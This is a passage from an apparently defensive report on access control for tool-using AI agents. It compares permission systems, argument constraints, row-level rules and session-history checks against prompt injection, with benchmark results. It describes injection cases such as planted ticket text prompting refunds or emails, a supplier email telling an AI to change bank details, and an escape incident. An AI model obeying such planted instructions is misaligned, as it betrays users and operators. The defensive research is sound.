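When there was no attack, the restricted agent completed 58% of its tasks and the unrestricted one 68%, a difference Alhindi reports as not statistically significant (*p* = 0.267). A gap at least this large would turn up about a quarter of the time even if the restriction made no difference. But with only 37 tasks, the test could easily miss a real drop in completion. The restriction could cause one because a model that sees a function may try to use it, and the task can fail when the kernel refuses. Removing the forbidden functions from the model's list as well might recover some of those tasks, though Alhindi didn't try it.

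The 7% also makes the permissions look more effective than they are. When the agent held every function, 358 attacks succeeded over the three runs. With the restriction, the kernel stopped 233 of those by refusing a function the attack needed. Another 90 failed without a refusal, for example because the model by chance ignored the planted text. Alhindi therefore ran a harsher test, simulating an attacker with full control of the agent by replacing the model with a script that carried out the user's task and then made every call the attacker's goal required. With every function available, the script succeeded in 248 of the 249 cases. With the restriction, the kernel stopped 181 of those 248, or 73%.

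The other 67 attacks used only functions that the user's own task needed. The same was true of every attack that got past the permissions when the model was making the decisions. About half of those used `send_money`, which the agent was allowed to use to pay a bill, to send money to the attacker. Permission to use the function doesn't limit who receives the money, which takes an argument constraint such as a list of approved payees. The permissions stopped a smaller share of the scripted attacks in banking (68%) than in Slack (80%), probably because stealing money and paying a bill both require the payment function.

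Alhindi took each task's permissions from AgentDojo's own solution to that task, and acknowledges that this is a best case. Someone who has to grant permissions before knowing the task would probably grant more. For instance, the shop knows a ticket has arrived but not whether it will require a refund. If the shop grants the refund tool to every session just in case, a planted request for a refund becomes another attack that uses only permitted functions.

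When the attacker controls only text, an ordinary proxy could refuse the same calls as seL4. The kernel is more useful against an attacker who can run code inside the agent and attack the software that checks the calls. Alhindi cites a July 2026 incident in which OpenAI models escaped from a test environment through a flaw in the proxy that was the environment's only way out. The prototype doesn't yet have the full benefit of seL4's proofs because it ran on an emulator, in a debugging version that the proofs don't cover.

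### Roles the agent picks up as it works

If the shop can't tell in advance which tools a ticket will need, it could let the agent ask for them along the way. *Progressive Skill Discovery as Access Control for Tool-Using LLM Agents* (Stettler, Girardet and colleagues, 2026) describes Skilder, a product that does this. At the start of a session, the agent sees four general tools and a short catalogue of roles, such as Tier 1 Support. It asks to "learn" a role, which loads that role's instructions and tools into the conversation. Skilder runs a call only if the tool belongs to a role the agent has learned, and answers any other call with an access-denied message.

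This resembles the session in Ferraiolo and colleagues' standard. The catalogue corresponds to the roles an administrator has assigned, and the learned roles correspond to the active ones. But learned roles stay active, so the agent's permissions can grow but not shrink during a session, as under MCP's procedure for adding scopes.

The agent also decides which roles to learn. A manipulated agent could learn every role in its catalogue, so the catalogue limits what an attacker can do. An administrator sets the catalogue before the session starts. Stettler and colleagues consider the worry that someone could tell the agent to learn the administrator role, and they answer that a support session's catalogue doesn't contain that role. This is right, but if the shop puts a refund role in the catalogue, an attacker can plant an instruction to learn that role and then issue a refund. The log would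 show that the agent had learned the role, which would help an investigator.

Stettler and colleagues tested the design in 13 scenarios with six models, including Claude Opus 4.7 and GPT-5.5. In one scenario, a user gets ordinary support and then claims that a manager has verbally approved deleting some accounts. When the models could see all the tools, they carried out a destructive call in 23 of 60 trials. With Skilder, whose catalogue contained only the support role, they did so in none. A coordinator that passed work to specialist agents also scored perfectly after the researchers removed its administrator specialist. The protection came from removing access to the dangerous tools, which doesn't require Skilder.

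In another scenario, the request was for a $1,200 refund, but the support role had a $500 limit. No refund above $500 went through under Skilder in 60 trials, but the limit was really tested only once, because only one model attempted such a refund. In nine trials, a model issued a $500 refund that nobody had requested, which the limit allowed.

Some models had trouble with the extra steps. On four kinds of ordinary support task, the models tested passed 198 of 240 trials with Skilder and 229 with all the tools visible. Claude Haiku 4.5, Gemma 4 31B and GPT-5.5 passed all their trials with Skilder. Most of the shortfall came from Qwen 3.5 and Ministral 3, which often failed to complete the discovery steps. Opus 4.7 failed three of its ten refund trials with Skilder, partly because it treated the shop's legitimate policy, which had arrived as the result of a tool call, as a prompt injection.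 A model that tends to reject instructions in tool results may also reject rules its operator delivers that way.

Loading tools on demand saves tokens when an agent has many tools. With 225 tools, a single customer lookup took 9,084 tokens with Skilder and 51,330 with the full list. The two were about equal at 30 tools, so with the support agent's 12 tools, Skilder would use more tokens than it saved.

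Stettler and colleagues work for the company that makes Skilder, and they tested a simulation of its permission checks on invented data. They report that the checks blocked every forbidden call that reached them. As in Uppala's experiment, this follows from the design if the code has no errors. The task results are more useful to a buyer because they show which models can work within the restrictions.

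### Do newer models make these rules unnecessary?

Most of the models in these experiments are old or small, and developers have since trained models to resist planted instructions. If a model ignores those instructions, a rule that blocks the resulting calls has no effect. Recent tests give this objection some support.

*It's a TRAP! Task-Redirecting Agent Persuasion Benchmark for Web Agents* (Korgul, Yang and colleagues, 2025) planted persuasive text in copies of six popular websites and counted a success each time an agent clicked the attacker's link or button. Across six models, the attacks succeeded 25% of the time, ranging from 13% for GPT-5 to 43% for DeepSeek-R1. All six models are now old. *Domain-Conditioned Safety in Frontier Computer-Using Agents* (2026) tried ten templates based on the same techniques on Claude Sonnet 4.6 and GPT-5.4, and none worked. The websites and tasks were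 different, so this doesn't overturn the earlier result, but it is consistent with models having generally improved.

Human attackers have also had less success. Gray Swan, an AI security company, runs the IPI Arena, a public competition in which people try to hijack agents built on leading models. *Beam Model Technical Report* (2026) lists rounds up to August 2026, with attacks that aim at serious harm such as leaked data or unwanted payments. *How Vulnerable Are AI Agents to Indirect Prompt Injections?* (Dziemian, Lin and colleagues, 2026) analysed 272,000 attempts by 464 participants against 13 models. The success rate ranged from 0.5% against Claude Opus 4.5 to 8.5% against Gemini 2.5 Pro. *Scaling Adaptive Prompt Injection Attacks with Agent Swarms* (Kurakin, Karande and colleagues, 2026) reports that by autumn 2026, attacks replayed from the arena succeeded less than 1% of the time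 against recent Gemini models and some Claude models.

Developers publish their own figures. Cross (2026), in *GPT-6 Sol Scores 97.13% on Indirect Injection Defense*, reports OpenAI's October score for that model, so just under 3% of the test's attacks succeeded.

A low rate per attempt is less reassuring when the attacker can keep trying. If each attempt succeeds with probability *p*, independently of the others, the chance of at least one success in *n* attempts is

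1 − (1 − *p*)ⁿ

If each attempt has a 0.5% chance of success, 200 attempts have a 63% chance of at least one success, and the shop lets anyone open 200 tickets. This calculation assumes that attempts are independent, but a model that has resisted one version of a trick will often resist the next. VentureBeat gives figures from Anthropic's February 2026 system card for Claude Opus 4.6. When the model operated a computer through its graphical interface without extra safeguards, a single attempt succeeded 17.8% of the time. If attempts were independent, at least one success in 200 would be nearly certain, but the measured rate was 78.6%, or 57.1% with safeguards. In a restricted coding environment, the same model resisted all 200 attempts, so a single success rate for a model can mislead.

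Kurakin and colleagues at Google DeepMind tested attacks run by a capable AI system. Sixteen agents worked together on each attack, sharing notes and revising the planted text after seeing how the target responded, for up to 320 attempts. In one of the 100 scenarios, a user books a tutoring session and the planted text is meant to make the target agent record medical readings. The table gives the share of scenarios in which at least one attempt succeeded when Gemini 4 Argon was the attacker.

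| Target model | Within 150 attempts | Within 320 attempts |
|---|---|---|
| Gemini 4 Argon | 13% | 34% |
| Gemini 3.8 Flash | 66% | 90% |
| Kimi K3 | 95% | 99% |
| GLM-5.3 | 99% | 99% |
| DeepSeek-V4.1-Flash | 99% | 99% |

These rates are not comparable with the arena's, which count each attempt separately. The planted requests were also mostly harmless, and a model might resist a request for money more often. Kurakin and colleagues had switched off the defences that normally surround the Gemini models. The results also depended heavily on the attacker's strength. Gemini 4 Argon resisted every attack by three weaker Gemini models within 150 attempts, so its resistance could look complete until a stronger attacker tries. The last three models in the table have downloadable weights, and a shop that chose one of them to save money would get very little resistance from the model itself.

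In every scenario, the attacker wanted the agent to call a tool from a different field than the user's task, such as a health tool during a tutoring booking. An agent allowed to use only tools from the task's own field could not have completed any of those calls, however persuasive the attacker's text. An attacker who knew of this limit would presumably target the permitted tools instead, as the attacks that still worked on Alhindi's agent did with `send_money`.

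## How can an agent be limited to particular records and actions?

Permission to use a payment tool does not limit who receives the money, and 67 scripted attacks got past Alhindi's tool permissions through gaps of this kind. *ToolFence* (Li, Cao and Xiao, 2026) reports a similar figure, based on comparing the calls each AgentDojo task requires with the calls each attack requires. In 61 of the 249 combinations in the banking and Slack parts, the task and the attack used the same tools and differed only in a value such as the recipient or the file. Across the whole benchmark, this was true of 85 of 629 combinations.

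Limiting an agent to particular records and actions requires argument constraints, which restrict the values it can pass to a tool, and resource-level permissions, which specify the records, files or accounts a permitted tool may access. When a tool takes a customer number, one rule can restrict both the argument and the records. When a tool takes a database query or a search phrase, the call doesn't identify the records it will return, so the limit has to apply where the records are stored.

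### Limits on records

A database can enforce a resource-level permission itself. In PostgreSQL, a widely used database, an administrator can attach a condition to a table, and the database applies it to every query. Suppose the shop's software begins work on Maria Lopez's ticket by recording 20417 as the current customer number, and the condition on the customer table is that a row's customer number must match the recorded one. If a manipulated agent then asks for every customer's address, the database returns only Maria's row.

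This row-level rule works however the agent words its query, but it depends on how the agent connects. PostgreSQL exempts administrators and, by default, the table's owner, so an agent that uses the owner's account sees all 40,000 rows. An agent that can send any database command might also change the current customer number, so the shop has to block it from changing that setting. The query results also don't indicate that rows have been filtered out. If a manager asks how many customers are waiting for refunds, the agent may count the only row it can see and report one customer.

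Relationship-based rules grant access by following links between people and things. Google's Zanzibar is the best-known system that does this. The shop could store two facts: this agent run is handling ticket 8812, and customer 20417 opened ticket 8812. A rule could then let whoever handles a ticket read the record of the customer who opened it. When the shop closes the ticket and deletes the first fact, the access ends without anyone editing a list of permissions. Links can also give access that nobody intended, for example when a new member of a group gains access to every folder ever shared with the group. Row security and relationship-based rules are both older than AI agents. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (2026), which proposes enforcing policy at the boundary between an agent and its tools, cites PostgreSQL's row security and Zanzibar.

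Many agents also search a company's documents and read the passages that best match a question. The search software should apply the user's access rights first, so that it searches only the documents the user may open. If it instead picks the ten best matches from all the documents and then removes the forbidden ones, it may have only two left, even though other permitted documents would have helped. Checking only the finished answer is too late, because the model has already read the forbidden text.

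Zhou and Zhang note that the position of a check determines which operations it can detect and which effects it can block. A check on tool calls can't monitor what a tool's program does while running, so some systems confine that program or intercept the web requests a browser sends. A model can also avoid a check by using other tools. In tests of two agent applications reported in *aiAuthZ* (Kodathala, 2026), the model carried out the sensitive action with the application's own shell, file and web tools, and never sent a request to the separate server that was meant to approve it.

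### Limits on arguments

That server, aiAuthZ, approves or refuses tool calls under a policy the agent can neither read nor change. It first checks whether the caller's role may use the tool. It then compares the arguments with lists of file paths, web addresses and email recipients, and caps how much data a single call can write. For example, if the list of permitted web addresses is empty, the server refuses every fetch, even for an employee who has permission to use the web tool.

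Such rules are easy to get wrong. A check on file paths has to resolve each path to the file's real location before comparing it with the list, because a path that starts in a permitted folder can use ".." to leave it. A limit on amounts applies to each call separately, so ten refunds just below the limit all pass. *NOMOS* (Yu, Kim and Choi, 2026) describes a test attack that splits a transfer into instalments of $10,000. To stop this, an amount rule needs a running total, which is a simple check on session history.

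Access rules also need to account for who is making the request. Kodathala took nine cases from a study in which researchers attacked live agents. A policy that checked only a tool call's arguments blocked four of them, while the full system, which also verifies a signature on each user's message, blocked all nine. In the other five cases, the attacker posed as the agent's owner and used a generally permitted tool. A policy that doesn't check identity has to allow such a call for everyone or for nobody. The arguments-only policy was Kodathala's own reconstruction of a rival design, so the comparison shows what checking identity adds but not how well the rival product works.

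### A policy for one ticket

The shop could use this policy for Maria Lopez's ticket:

```
Ticket 8812, customer 20417

allow read_ticket      if ticket = 8812
allow lookup_customer  if customer = 20417
allow send_email       if recipient = address on record for customer 20417
refuse everything else
```

The shop's software fills in both numbers before the agent reads the ticket. It takes the customer number from the account Maria Lopez used to open the ticket, not from what she typed, because anyone could type another customer's number. If the ticket arrived by email, the shop may have only the sender's address to identify the customer, and a stranger can forge that. The agent's reply would still go to the address on record, so the forger wouldn't receive it.

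Three calls show how the enforcement point applies the policy:

1. The agent calls `lookup_customer` for customer 20417. The enforcement point finds the rule for that tool and compares the numbers. They match, so the lookup runs and the agent receives the record.
2. Text planted in the ticket persuades the agent to call `lookup_customer` for customer 20418. The tool is permitted but the number doesn't match, and no other rule allows the call. The enforcement point returns an error without contacting the database, and the agent can carry on with the ticket.
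3. The agent calls `send_email` with an address that appears only in the planted text. This isn't the address on record for customer 20417, so the email is never sent, whatever it contains.

The number of combinations of tool and record within reach is now

3 × 1 = 3

compared with 120,000 when the shop restricted only the tools. The agent can still do harm within those three, for instance by giving Maria Lopez wrong information or copying a private staff note from her record into the email. If the ticket called for a refund, the shop could add a rule that the order must belong to customer 20417 and that the refund can't exceed the price paid. That rule would limit the loss, but it would still allow a refund that nobody had requested.

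### Writing the rules by hand

Someone at the shop can write this policy once, because every ticket has the same structure and only the numbers change. Handwritten rules are predictable and easy to inspect, but they fail when the writer doesn't foresee a legitimate request. If Maria Lopez has lost access to her old email account and asks for a reply at a new address, the policy blocks it.

Kodathala measured this drawback by testing a strict list of known payees on 20 combinations of task and attack from the banking part of AgentDojo. The two models, Anthropic's Fable 5 and Google's Gemini 3 Flash, were newer than those in most such experiments. Without any defence, the attack success rate was already 0% for both, so the list couldn't reduce it. But when there was no attack, the list lowered utility from 100% to 80% for both models because it blocked a legitimate first payment to a new payee.

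The test is too small to reliably estimate how much the list interferes with legitimate tasks. If one blocked payment accounts for 20 percentage points, there were probably only five different legitimate tasks. Fable 5 also dropped to 80% under a different defence, which marks outside text as untrusted and blocks no payments. The list did provide some security, since the server refused all seven calls the two models attempted that served the attacker. Kodathala acknowledges that, on this benchmark, the list does more harm than good for a model that already resists the attack. An operator who adopts it accepts some blocked legitimate work in exchange for protection against stronger attacks than the benchmark contains.

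### Generating rules from the user's request

A general assistant receives a different request each time, so nobody can write all its policies in advance. *Progent* (Shi, He and colleagues, 2025) uses a language model to write a policy for each request. The model receives the request and the list of tools, but no emails, web pages or other outside text, so planted text can't influence the first version of the policy. Each rule in the policy allows or forbids a tool under conditions on its arguments. Ordinary code then checks every call against these rules. A rule that forbids a call overrides one that allows it, and calls that match no rule are refused.

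The first version may be too narrow. If a worker tells the agent to "answer ticket 8812", the request contains no customer number, so the policy can't name the right customer until the agent has read the ticket. Progent lets the model propose a new policy after a tool returns a result, but by then the model may be reading a stranger's text. The system therefore compares the calls that the two policies allow. If *P* is the old policy, *P*′ the new one and *A* the set of calls a policy allows, the change takes effect automatically only when

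*A*(*P*′) ⊆ *A*(*P*)

A policy change needs no approval if the new policy allows nothing the old one didn't. Any other change needs approval from a person or from a setting chosen in advance. A solver, a program that can prove whether a condition holds for every possible value, compares the two policies, so a model misled by planted text can't widen the policy unnoticed. In the shop's case, adding permission to look up customer 20417 would need approval, but restricting email to the address on record would not if the policy already allowed email to anyone.

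On AgentDojo with OpenAI's gpt-4o, Progent cut the attack success rate from 39.9% to 1.0%. On Agent Security Bench (ASB), which covers ten kinds of agent, the rate fell from 70.3% to 3.9%. Utility on AgentDojo fell slightly, from 79.4% to 76.3%, according to figures Yu and colleagues quote from an earlier version of the Progent paper.

These results provide little evidence about the approval step, because Shi and colleagues approved every expansion automatically to represent a careless user. The solver's comparison therefore blocked nothing, and the low rates reflect how well the model wrote rules, even after it had read planted text. The first version of the policy, with no later changes, reduced attack success on AgentDojo to 2.5%.

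No attacks succeeded when a person reviewed the policies. But Shi and colleagues assumed that the reviewer would never allow payments to just anyone and would reject a malicious address, and a busy support worker may be less careful. Only 6% of policy changes needed approval, which keeps the number of prompts down. For AgentDojo, they also let the agent use non-sensitive read-only tools freely, so the experiment is better evidence about limiting payments and messages than about limiting which records an agent can read.

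### Specifying where each value must come from

Sometimes the user's request identifies the source of a value but not the value itself. A user who says "pay the bill in this file" hasn't named the payee, although the file does. Li and colleagues built ToolFence to handle such cases. A model that sees only the user's request and trusted descriptions of the tools decides how the system should check each argument:

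- It can require an exact value from the user's request or from a trusted record, such as "$100".
- It can require a value that a particular tool returned, such as the account number in the bill file.
- It can leave a harmless argument, such as the wording of a greeting, to the agent.

Each permission also limits how often the agent can use it. If the user authorizes one payment of $100 to a company called BillPay, code outside the model blocks the same payment to anyone else and a second payment to BillPay. When the agent needs a permission that the first plan left out, a separate model reviews the request. The reviewing model receives the name of the requested tool and the required source of each argument, but not the values.

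With Alibaba's Qwen3-max as the agent, ToolFence reduced attack success on AgentDojo from 21.2% to 0%, while utility without attacks fell from 66.3% to 64.3%. During attacks, utility rose from 55.2% to 62.1%, probably because an agent that receives a refusal often returns to the user's task. In a sample of 200 cases, ToolFence increased the average run time from 6.3 to 10.3 seconds.

Li and colleagues also removed parts of the system one at a time and tested each version on ASB with Meta's Llama 3.3 70B. Attacks succeeded 5.1% of the time against the complete system and 45.4% of the time against an unprotected agent. Without the checks on argument values, the rate was 24.0%, which is the most direct evidence here that limiting tools alone isn't enough. Removing the model that grants missing permissions hardly changed attack success, but it cut utility during attacks from 44.3% to 35.8%, below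 the unprotected agent's 40.1%. A policy fixed at the start can therefore block so many legitimate steps that an agent under attack is less useful than it would be with no defence.

The reviewing model, which grants extra permissions, can also be a weakness. AgentLAB, a benchmark of longer attacks, spreads planted text over several emails, calendar entries and files, so that the attacker's action looks like a necessary step in the user's task. With ToolFence, the success rate of these attacks fell from 76.3% to 29.4% against Qwen3-max, and was 38.3% against Llama. Li and colleagues attribute some of ToolFence's failures to the reviewing model granting overly broad permissions.

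A further test examined 551 proposed calls. The researchers had created many of them by using a permission at the wrong stage of a task or more often than allowed. Five unauthorized calls passed all the checks, all from one banking task in which the user's own request gave the attacker's account number as the new landlord's. No check on the source of a value can catch this, because the value came from the user.

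### Compiling rules from a written policy

Many companies have written rules for their staff, such as confirming a customer's identity before changing an order. Yu and colleagues at the company Corners built NOMOS, which turns such a document into rules on an agent's tool calls. A language model reads the document five times and proposes rules, each made up of a tool and a condition from a fixed list. Ordinary code removes defective rules, keeps those that appear in a majority of the readings, and enforces them while the agent works. The code relies only on tool results and the user's own messages, so a manipulated agent can't get a payment through by claiming that the user approved it.

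Many of the model's proposals would have failed in use. For example, the model turned the instruction to authenticate customers before doing anything else into a rule that blocked every tool until the customer was authenticated. The rule also blocked the two tools that perform authentication, so no conversation could have got past it. The code repaired or rejected 37% of the 79 proposals for an airline's policy and 13% of the 53 for a retailer's, for defects of this general kind. When Yu and colleagues switched off all the checks in a separate test, 8 of the 14 resulting rules for the airline and 3 of the 5 for the retailer couldn't work.

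These checks can't detect a workable rule that misstates the policy. In a telecom example, the policy required staff to confirm that a bill was overdue before requesting payment, but the model turned this into a ban on requesting payment while a bill was overdue. Yu and colleagues caught the mistake by replaying the rule against records of earlier conversations. It would have blocked 47 of the 49 payment requests made in successful runs. A shop could test a new policy on last month's tickets in the same way.

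NOMOS also reduces errors that agents make without an attacker. On τ²-bench, which simulates customer service under written policies, 66.3% of the changes an unprotected airline agent made broke the rules that Yu and colleagues checked, compared with 2.6% with NOMOS. The airline agent also completed more tasks with NOMOS (47.6% compared with 39.2%), although this difference could be due to chance. For the retail agent, violations fell from 30.8% to 6.9%, with no significant change in completed tasks.

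The results against planted instructions depended on the kind of work. AgentDojo has no written policies, so Yu and colleagues wrote a page of policy for each of its four parts. The banking page produced three rules, and the most important was that money may go only to someone the user has named or someone in the account's transaction history. Attack success in banking fell from 46.5% to 0%. Utility without attacks also fell, from 79.2% to 70.8%, but with only 16 tasks that difference could be due to chance.

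In the Slack part, attack success fell from 70.5% to 0%, but utility also fell, from 90.5% to 14.3%. Users there often ask the agent to act on something it has to find by reading, such as an article a colleague has posted. The rules allowed only links, channels and people that the user had named, so they blocked the legitimate link along with the attacker's. The shop's support agent is easier to restrict because its software can identify the customer who opened the ticket and look up the right address before the agent reads anything.

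The 0% in banking also needs qualifying. In 8 of 288 protected runs, the agent sent an injected payment to someone already in the user's transaction history instead of to the attacker's account. The policy allowed these payments and the benchmark didn't count them as successful attacks, but the user still lost money to payments they hadn't requested. Yu and colleagues also warn that an attacker could get into the history as a known payee by sending the user an unexpected payment. AgentDojo's attackers can't do this, so its scores don't include the risk.

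Yu and colleagues also ran Progent on the same banking tasks, using Google's Gemma 4 26B both to run the agent and to write the policies. Of the 16 attacks that still succeeded, 12 came from two tasks in which the user asked the agent to pay a bill without naming the payee's account. A policy written from that request can't specify the right recipient. NOMOS stopped the attacks on these tasks, but when the payee's account number appeared only in the bill, it also refused the legitimate payment.

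The table gives the attack success rate and the utility without attacks, before and after each system was added.

| System and tester | Source of the rules | Test | Attack success | Utility |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| aiAuthZ, Kodathala | Written by hand | Banking, Fable 5 and Gemini 3 Flash | 0% → 0% | 100% → 80% |
| Progent, Shi and colleagues | User's request | AgentDojo, gpt-4o | 39.9% → 1.0% | 79.4% → 76.3% |
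| Progent, Yu and colleagues | User's request | Banking, Gemma 4 26B | 46.5% → 5.6% | 79.2% → 62.5% |
| ToolFence, Li and colleagues | User's request | AgentDojo, Qwen3-max | 21.2% → 0% | 66.3% → 64.3% |
| NOMOS, Yu and colleagues | Written policy | Banking, Gemma 4 26B | 46.5% → 0% | 79.2% → 70.8% |
| NOMOS, Yu and colleagues | Written policy | Slack, Gemma 4 26B | 70.5% → 0% | 90.5% → 14.3% |

The rows can't be used to rank the systems, because the agents and tasks differ. Only the Progent and NOMOS results on banking come from matching conditions, and Yu and colleagues had an interest in the outcome. They have published their rules but not their software, so other researchers can't repeat the NOMOS runs.

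### Outdated rules and rights that are too broad

A correct rule can become wrong while the agent is working. If the ticket's policy stores Maria Lopez's email address when the ticket opens, and she changes it an hour later, the reply goes to the old address. Looking up her current address when sending the reply avoids this. Document search has a similar problem when it keeps its own copy of who may open each file and updates it only overnight.

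Approvals can also become outdated. NOMOS treats a user's confirmation as valid for one attempt. In one test, a booking failed because of a formatting error and the agent tried again without asking, so the system refused the second attempt. Yu and colleagues argue that a retry may differ from what the user approved. However, the user has to answer an extra question even when nothing has changed. ToolFence keeps the pattern of an approved permission and reuses it in later sessions with new values, which halved the number of reviews in one test. If the first approval was a mistake, later sessions could repeat it.

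Suppose a support worker moves to another department while the agent is working on the worker's behalf. The agent's next lookup fails if each service checks the worker's current rights on every call. If a service instead relies on a decision from the start of the session, the agent keeps its access, as Saltzer and Schroeder warned. Checking every call still can't remove a record that the model has already read, so the shop would also have to end the session and discard the agent's context and saved notes.

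Kodathala's system limits the delay by tying every call to the user's latest signed message, which expires after a limited time. The agent then can't act until the user sends another message. This suits a conversation, but it would interrupt an agent that answers tickets overnight.

The user's own rights may also be too broad. If a support worker can open all 40,000 customer records, a row-level rule based on that worker's identity would still let the agent read all of them. Document search can make old sharing mistakes more serious. A salary spreadsheet shared with the whole company years ago may have gone unnoticed, but an agent asked about pay could find it in seconds, and the filter would correctly allow it because the user has permission to open it.

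Kodathala notes that when an agent follows planted text using the user's own authority, verifying the user's identity doesn't help, and the only remaining defenses are limits on the arguments and number of calls. The worked policy ties access to the ticket rather than to the worker's rights, which is possible because the ticket concerns one customer. If a manager asks for a summary of all of this month's complaints, the agent may need thousands of records, and a rule that allowed only one would make the task impossible.

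## Can actions that are each permitted still add up to a leak?

A policy limited to one customer can't cover a manager's request for a summary of all of this month's complaints. Suppose the manager also asks the support agent to email the summary to an outside consultant. For this job, the shop lets the agent read the month's tickets, look up the customers who wrote them and send email to outside addresses. The agent then does the following:

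1. It reads the tickets. In one of them, a stranger has planted a request for a list of the customers' names and phone numbers.
2. It looks up the customers and compiles the list.
3. It emails the list to an address that appears in the planted text.

The enforcement point allows every call because the shop has permitted each of these actions. The leak comes from combining them. An argument constraint could limit the recipient to the consultant, which would keep the list from the stranger. But the agent could still send it to the consultant, who doesn't need customers' phone numbers. To prevent that, code outside the model has to track what the agent has already done or where the email's contents came from.

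### Spotting the dangerous combination

The programmer who coined the term "prompt injection" offers a quick way to recognise agents at risk. Willison (2025), in *The lethal trifecta for AI agents*, lists three properties that together let an attacker steal data:

- access to private data
- exposure to untrusted content, meaning any text or image an attacker could control
- a way to communicate externally

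The support agent has all three properties. Loading an image or showing a link counts as external communication, and data left this way in the SalesBleed case. Willison lists 17 attacks of this kind on AI products since April 2023 and notes that vendors usually responded by blocking the route the data took out. Users can recreate the problem by combining tools from different MCP servers, and then no vendor can fix it. A single tool can be enough, since an email tool can read private messages, receive text from strangers and send email.

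Meta's *Agents Rule of Two* (2025) turns the warning into a design rule. Until models can reliably detect and refuse prompt injection, an agent should have no more than two of these properties within a session: it processes untrustworthy input, can access sensitive systems or private data, and can change something or communicate externally. An agent that needs all three in one session should not work unsupervised. The rule covers harmful actions such as an unwanted refund, as well as the data theft described by the trifecta.

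The shop can apply the rule in three ways. It can't keep strangers' text away from an agent that answers tickets, and withholding customer records would rule out most useful replies. The practical choice is to restrict what the agent sends, either by having a person approve each draft or by allowing email only to the address on record, as the one-ticket policy does.

An agent can also change which two properties it has. In one of Meta's examples, an agent starts by browsing the internet, then permanently loses the ability to communicate when it opens internal systems. The complaints summary can't be handled this way, because the agent has to read strangers' text, use private records and send the result outside. That task would need a person's approval, and Meta acknowledges that people sometimes confirm a warning without reading it. The rule can be used to compare designs, but Meta gives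 no measurements of how many attacks it prevents.

### When the properties are spread over a team

A company could satisfy the Rule of Two by dividing work among several agents, each with only two of the properties. To test whether this is safe, Alhindi simulated a team of agents that pays a small firm's suppliers. An email agent reads supplier messages, an invoice agent checks invoices against the firm's records, an approval agent approves payments and a payment agent makes them. A coordinator assigns the work and maintains the bank's list of payees. Each agent on its own satisfies the rule. The email agent, for instance, reads strangers' text but can't see the firm's records or pay anyone.

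The agents pass text to one another, however. They do this directly when they hand over work, and indirectly through a shared ledger that some agents write to and others read. Alhindi's check maps these paths before the team runs. It finds the set *U* of agents that untrusted text can reach, the set *P* that private data can reach and the set *C* that can change something or send something out. The team breaks the rule if at least one agent is in all three sets:

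*U* ∩ *P* ∩ *C* ≠ ∅

Every agent except the email agent was in all three. Because seL4 enforces the same specification that the check reads, the agents can't pass text along a path that isn't on the map.

To test this danger, Alhindi sent the team a malicious email from a supplier's usual address, as if an attacker had taken over the supplier's mailbox. It contained a genuine invoice and a note with instructions for any AI assistant to replace the supplier's bank account details before approving the invoice. In 23 of 40 runs, the email and invoice agents passed the note on to the coordinator. In 7 runs, the coordinator changed the supplier's account, and in one of those it also replaced the accounts of the other two suppliers. No money went to the attacker because the approval for each invoice still named the old account, but the next payment would have used the new one.

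Alhindi then replaced the email agent with a parser, an ordinary program that extracts the invoice number, order number, total and supplier and discards everything else. In another 40 runs, the note never reached an agent and no account changed. This is strong evidence that the parser closed that path, though the experiment used one attack email, one team and gpt-4o-mini, an old and small model. A parser suits invoices because they have a few predictable fields, but an agent can't answer a complaint from its ticket number and date. If the agents need a stranger's words, the designer has to take private data or the power to act away from the agents those words can reach, or cut the links between them.

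### Judging a call by the session's history

A session history check can allow an agent to read private records or send email, but not both. A session-level grant is fixed at the start, so every call has to pass the same test. With a history check, the result depends on what the agent has already done, so the check can block an email that it would have allowed before the agent read private records.

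Muruaga (2026), in *Bounded Agents*, builds such a check into the definition of an agent's permissions. A scope *S* = (*R*, *A*, *D*, *X*) has four parts:

- *R* is the set of resources the agent may use, such as this month's tickets and the customer table.
- *A* is the set of permitted action types, such as reading a record or sending a message outside the company.
- *D* is the set of data classes it may handle, such as public or confidential.
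- *X* is the set of forbidden combinations of action types.

If *X* contains the pair "read a record" and "send outside", the agent may do either of them but not both in one session. The enforcement point refuses whichever action comes second. It also keeps the history, so a manipulated agent can't erase it.

When one agent delegates work to another, the second agent's scope combines the first agent's scope with the limits of its own role:

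*S*₁ ⊓ *S*₂ = (*R*₁ ∩ *R*₂, *A*₁ ∩ *A*₂, *D*₁ ∩ *D*₂, *X*₁ ∪ *X*₂)

The helper may use only the resources, actions and data classes that both scopes allow, and the prohibitions from both apply. If a coordinator may read and send, and a helper's role allows it to read and delete, the helper may only read when working for the coordinator. Prohibitions can't be lost when work is delegated, as the read-only restriction was in the earlier example of the emailed payment request. The agents also share one history, so the coordinator can't read a record and have a helper send it.

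According to a theorem, the history check prevents every forbidden outcome, such as sending customer data to a stranger, if each of those outcomes requires both action types in at least one pair from *X*. A sequence of calls that produced a forbidden outcome would have to include both actions of such a pair. When the agent attempted the later action, the earlier one would already be in the history, so the enforcement point would refuse the call.

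The guarantee holds only if somebody has listed every dangerous pair in *X* and assigned every tool to the right action type. The proof shows only that the code applies the list correctly. The checks also have to run one at a time, because if two agents act at once, one might read and the other send before the history records either action.

Some forbidden outcomes take more than two steps. An agent could read a record, copy it into a shared document and then send the document to a colleague without performing any forbidden pair of actions. Muruaga therefore also allows rules that forbid longer sequences of actions in a particular order.

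The complaints summary is a harder case because the job requires both reading private records and sending a message outside. Muruaga's system lets the person who starts the session declare a task that needs both actions, which removes that pair from *X* before the agent begins. The theorem then covers only the remaining pairs, so the shop has to either block the summary or give up this protection for the task that could cause the leak. The shop could instead define narrower action types, such as "read a complaint" and "read a phone number", and forbid only the combination of reading a phone number and sending a message outside. But if one tool returns the whole customer record, the shop would have to split that tool in two.

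### What the history check stopped

Muruaga tested the check on InjecAgent, a benchmark with 544 attacks that steal data and 510 that do direct harm, such as making an unwanted payment. The test did not run a model. It assumed that the agent had already read the planted text and was about to make the tool call the attacker wanted, then checked whether the rules blocked it, so without rules every attack succeeds by definition.

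| Rules | Data theft succeeds | Direct harm succeeds |
|---|---|---|
| None | 100% | 100% |
| Complete list of forbidden pairs | 0% | 60.4% |
| One pair missing | 39.9% | 82.0% |

Leaving one pair off the list let through two in five data thefts. A complete list is much easier to write for a benchmark, whose attacks are known in advance, than for a working shop. Even with the complete list, most of the direct-harm attacks succeeded because they need only one permitted action. A fraudulent refund, for example, needs no suspicious earlier step. Preventing it takes an argument constraint or a person's approval.

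Misclassifying tools has a similar effect. On Agent Security Bench, 60 of 200 "stealthy" attacks got through. Two types of data-export tool had the action type "write" instead of "send outside", so the rule against reading and then sending didn't apply to them.

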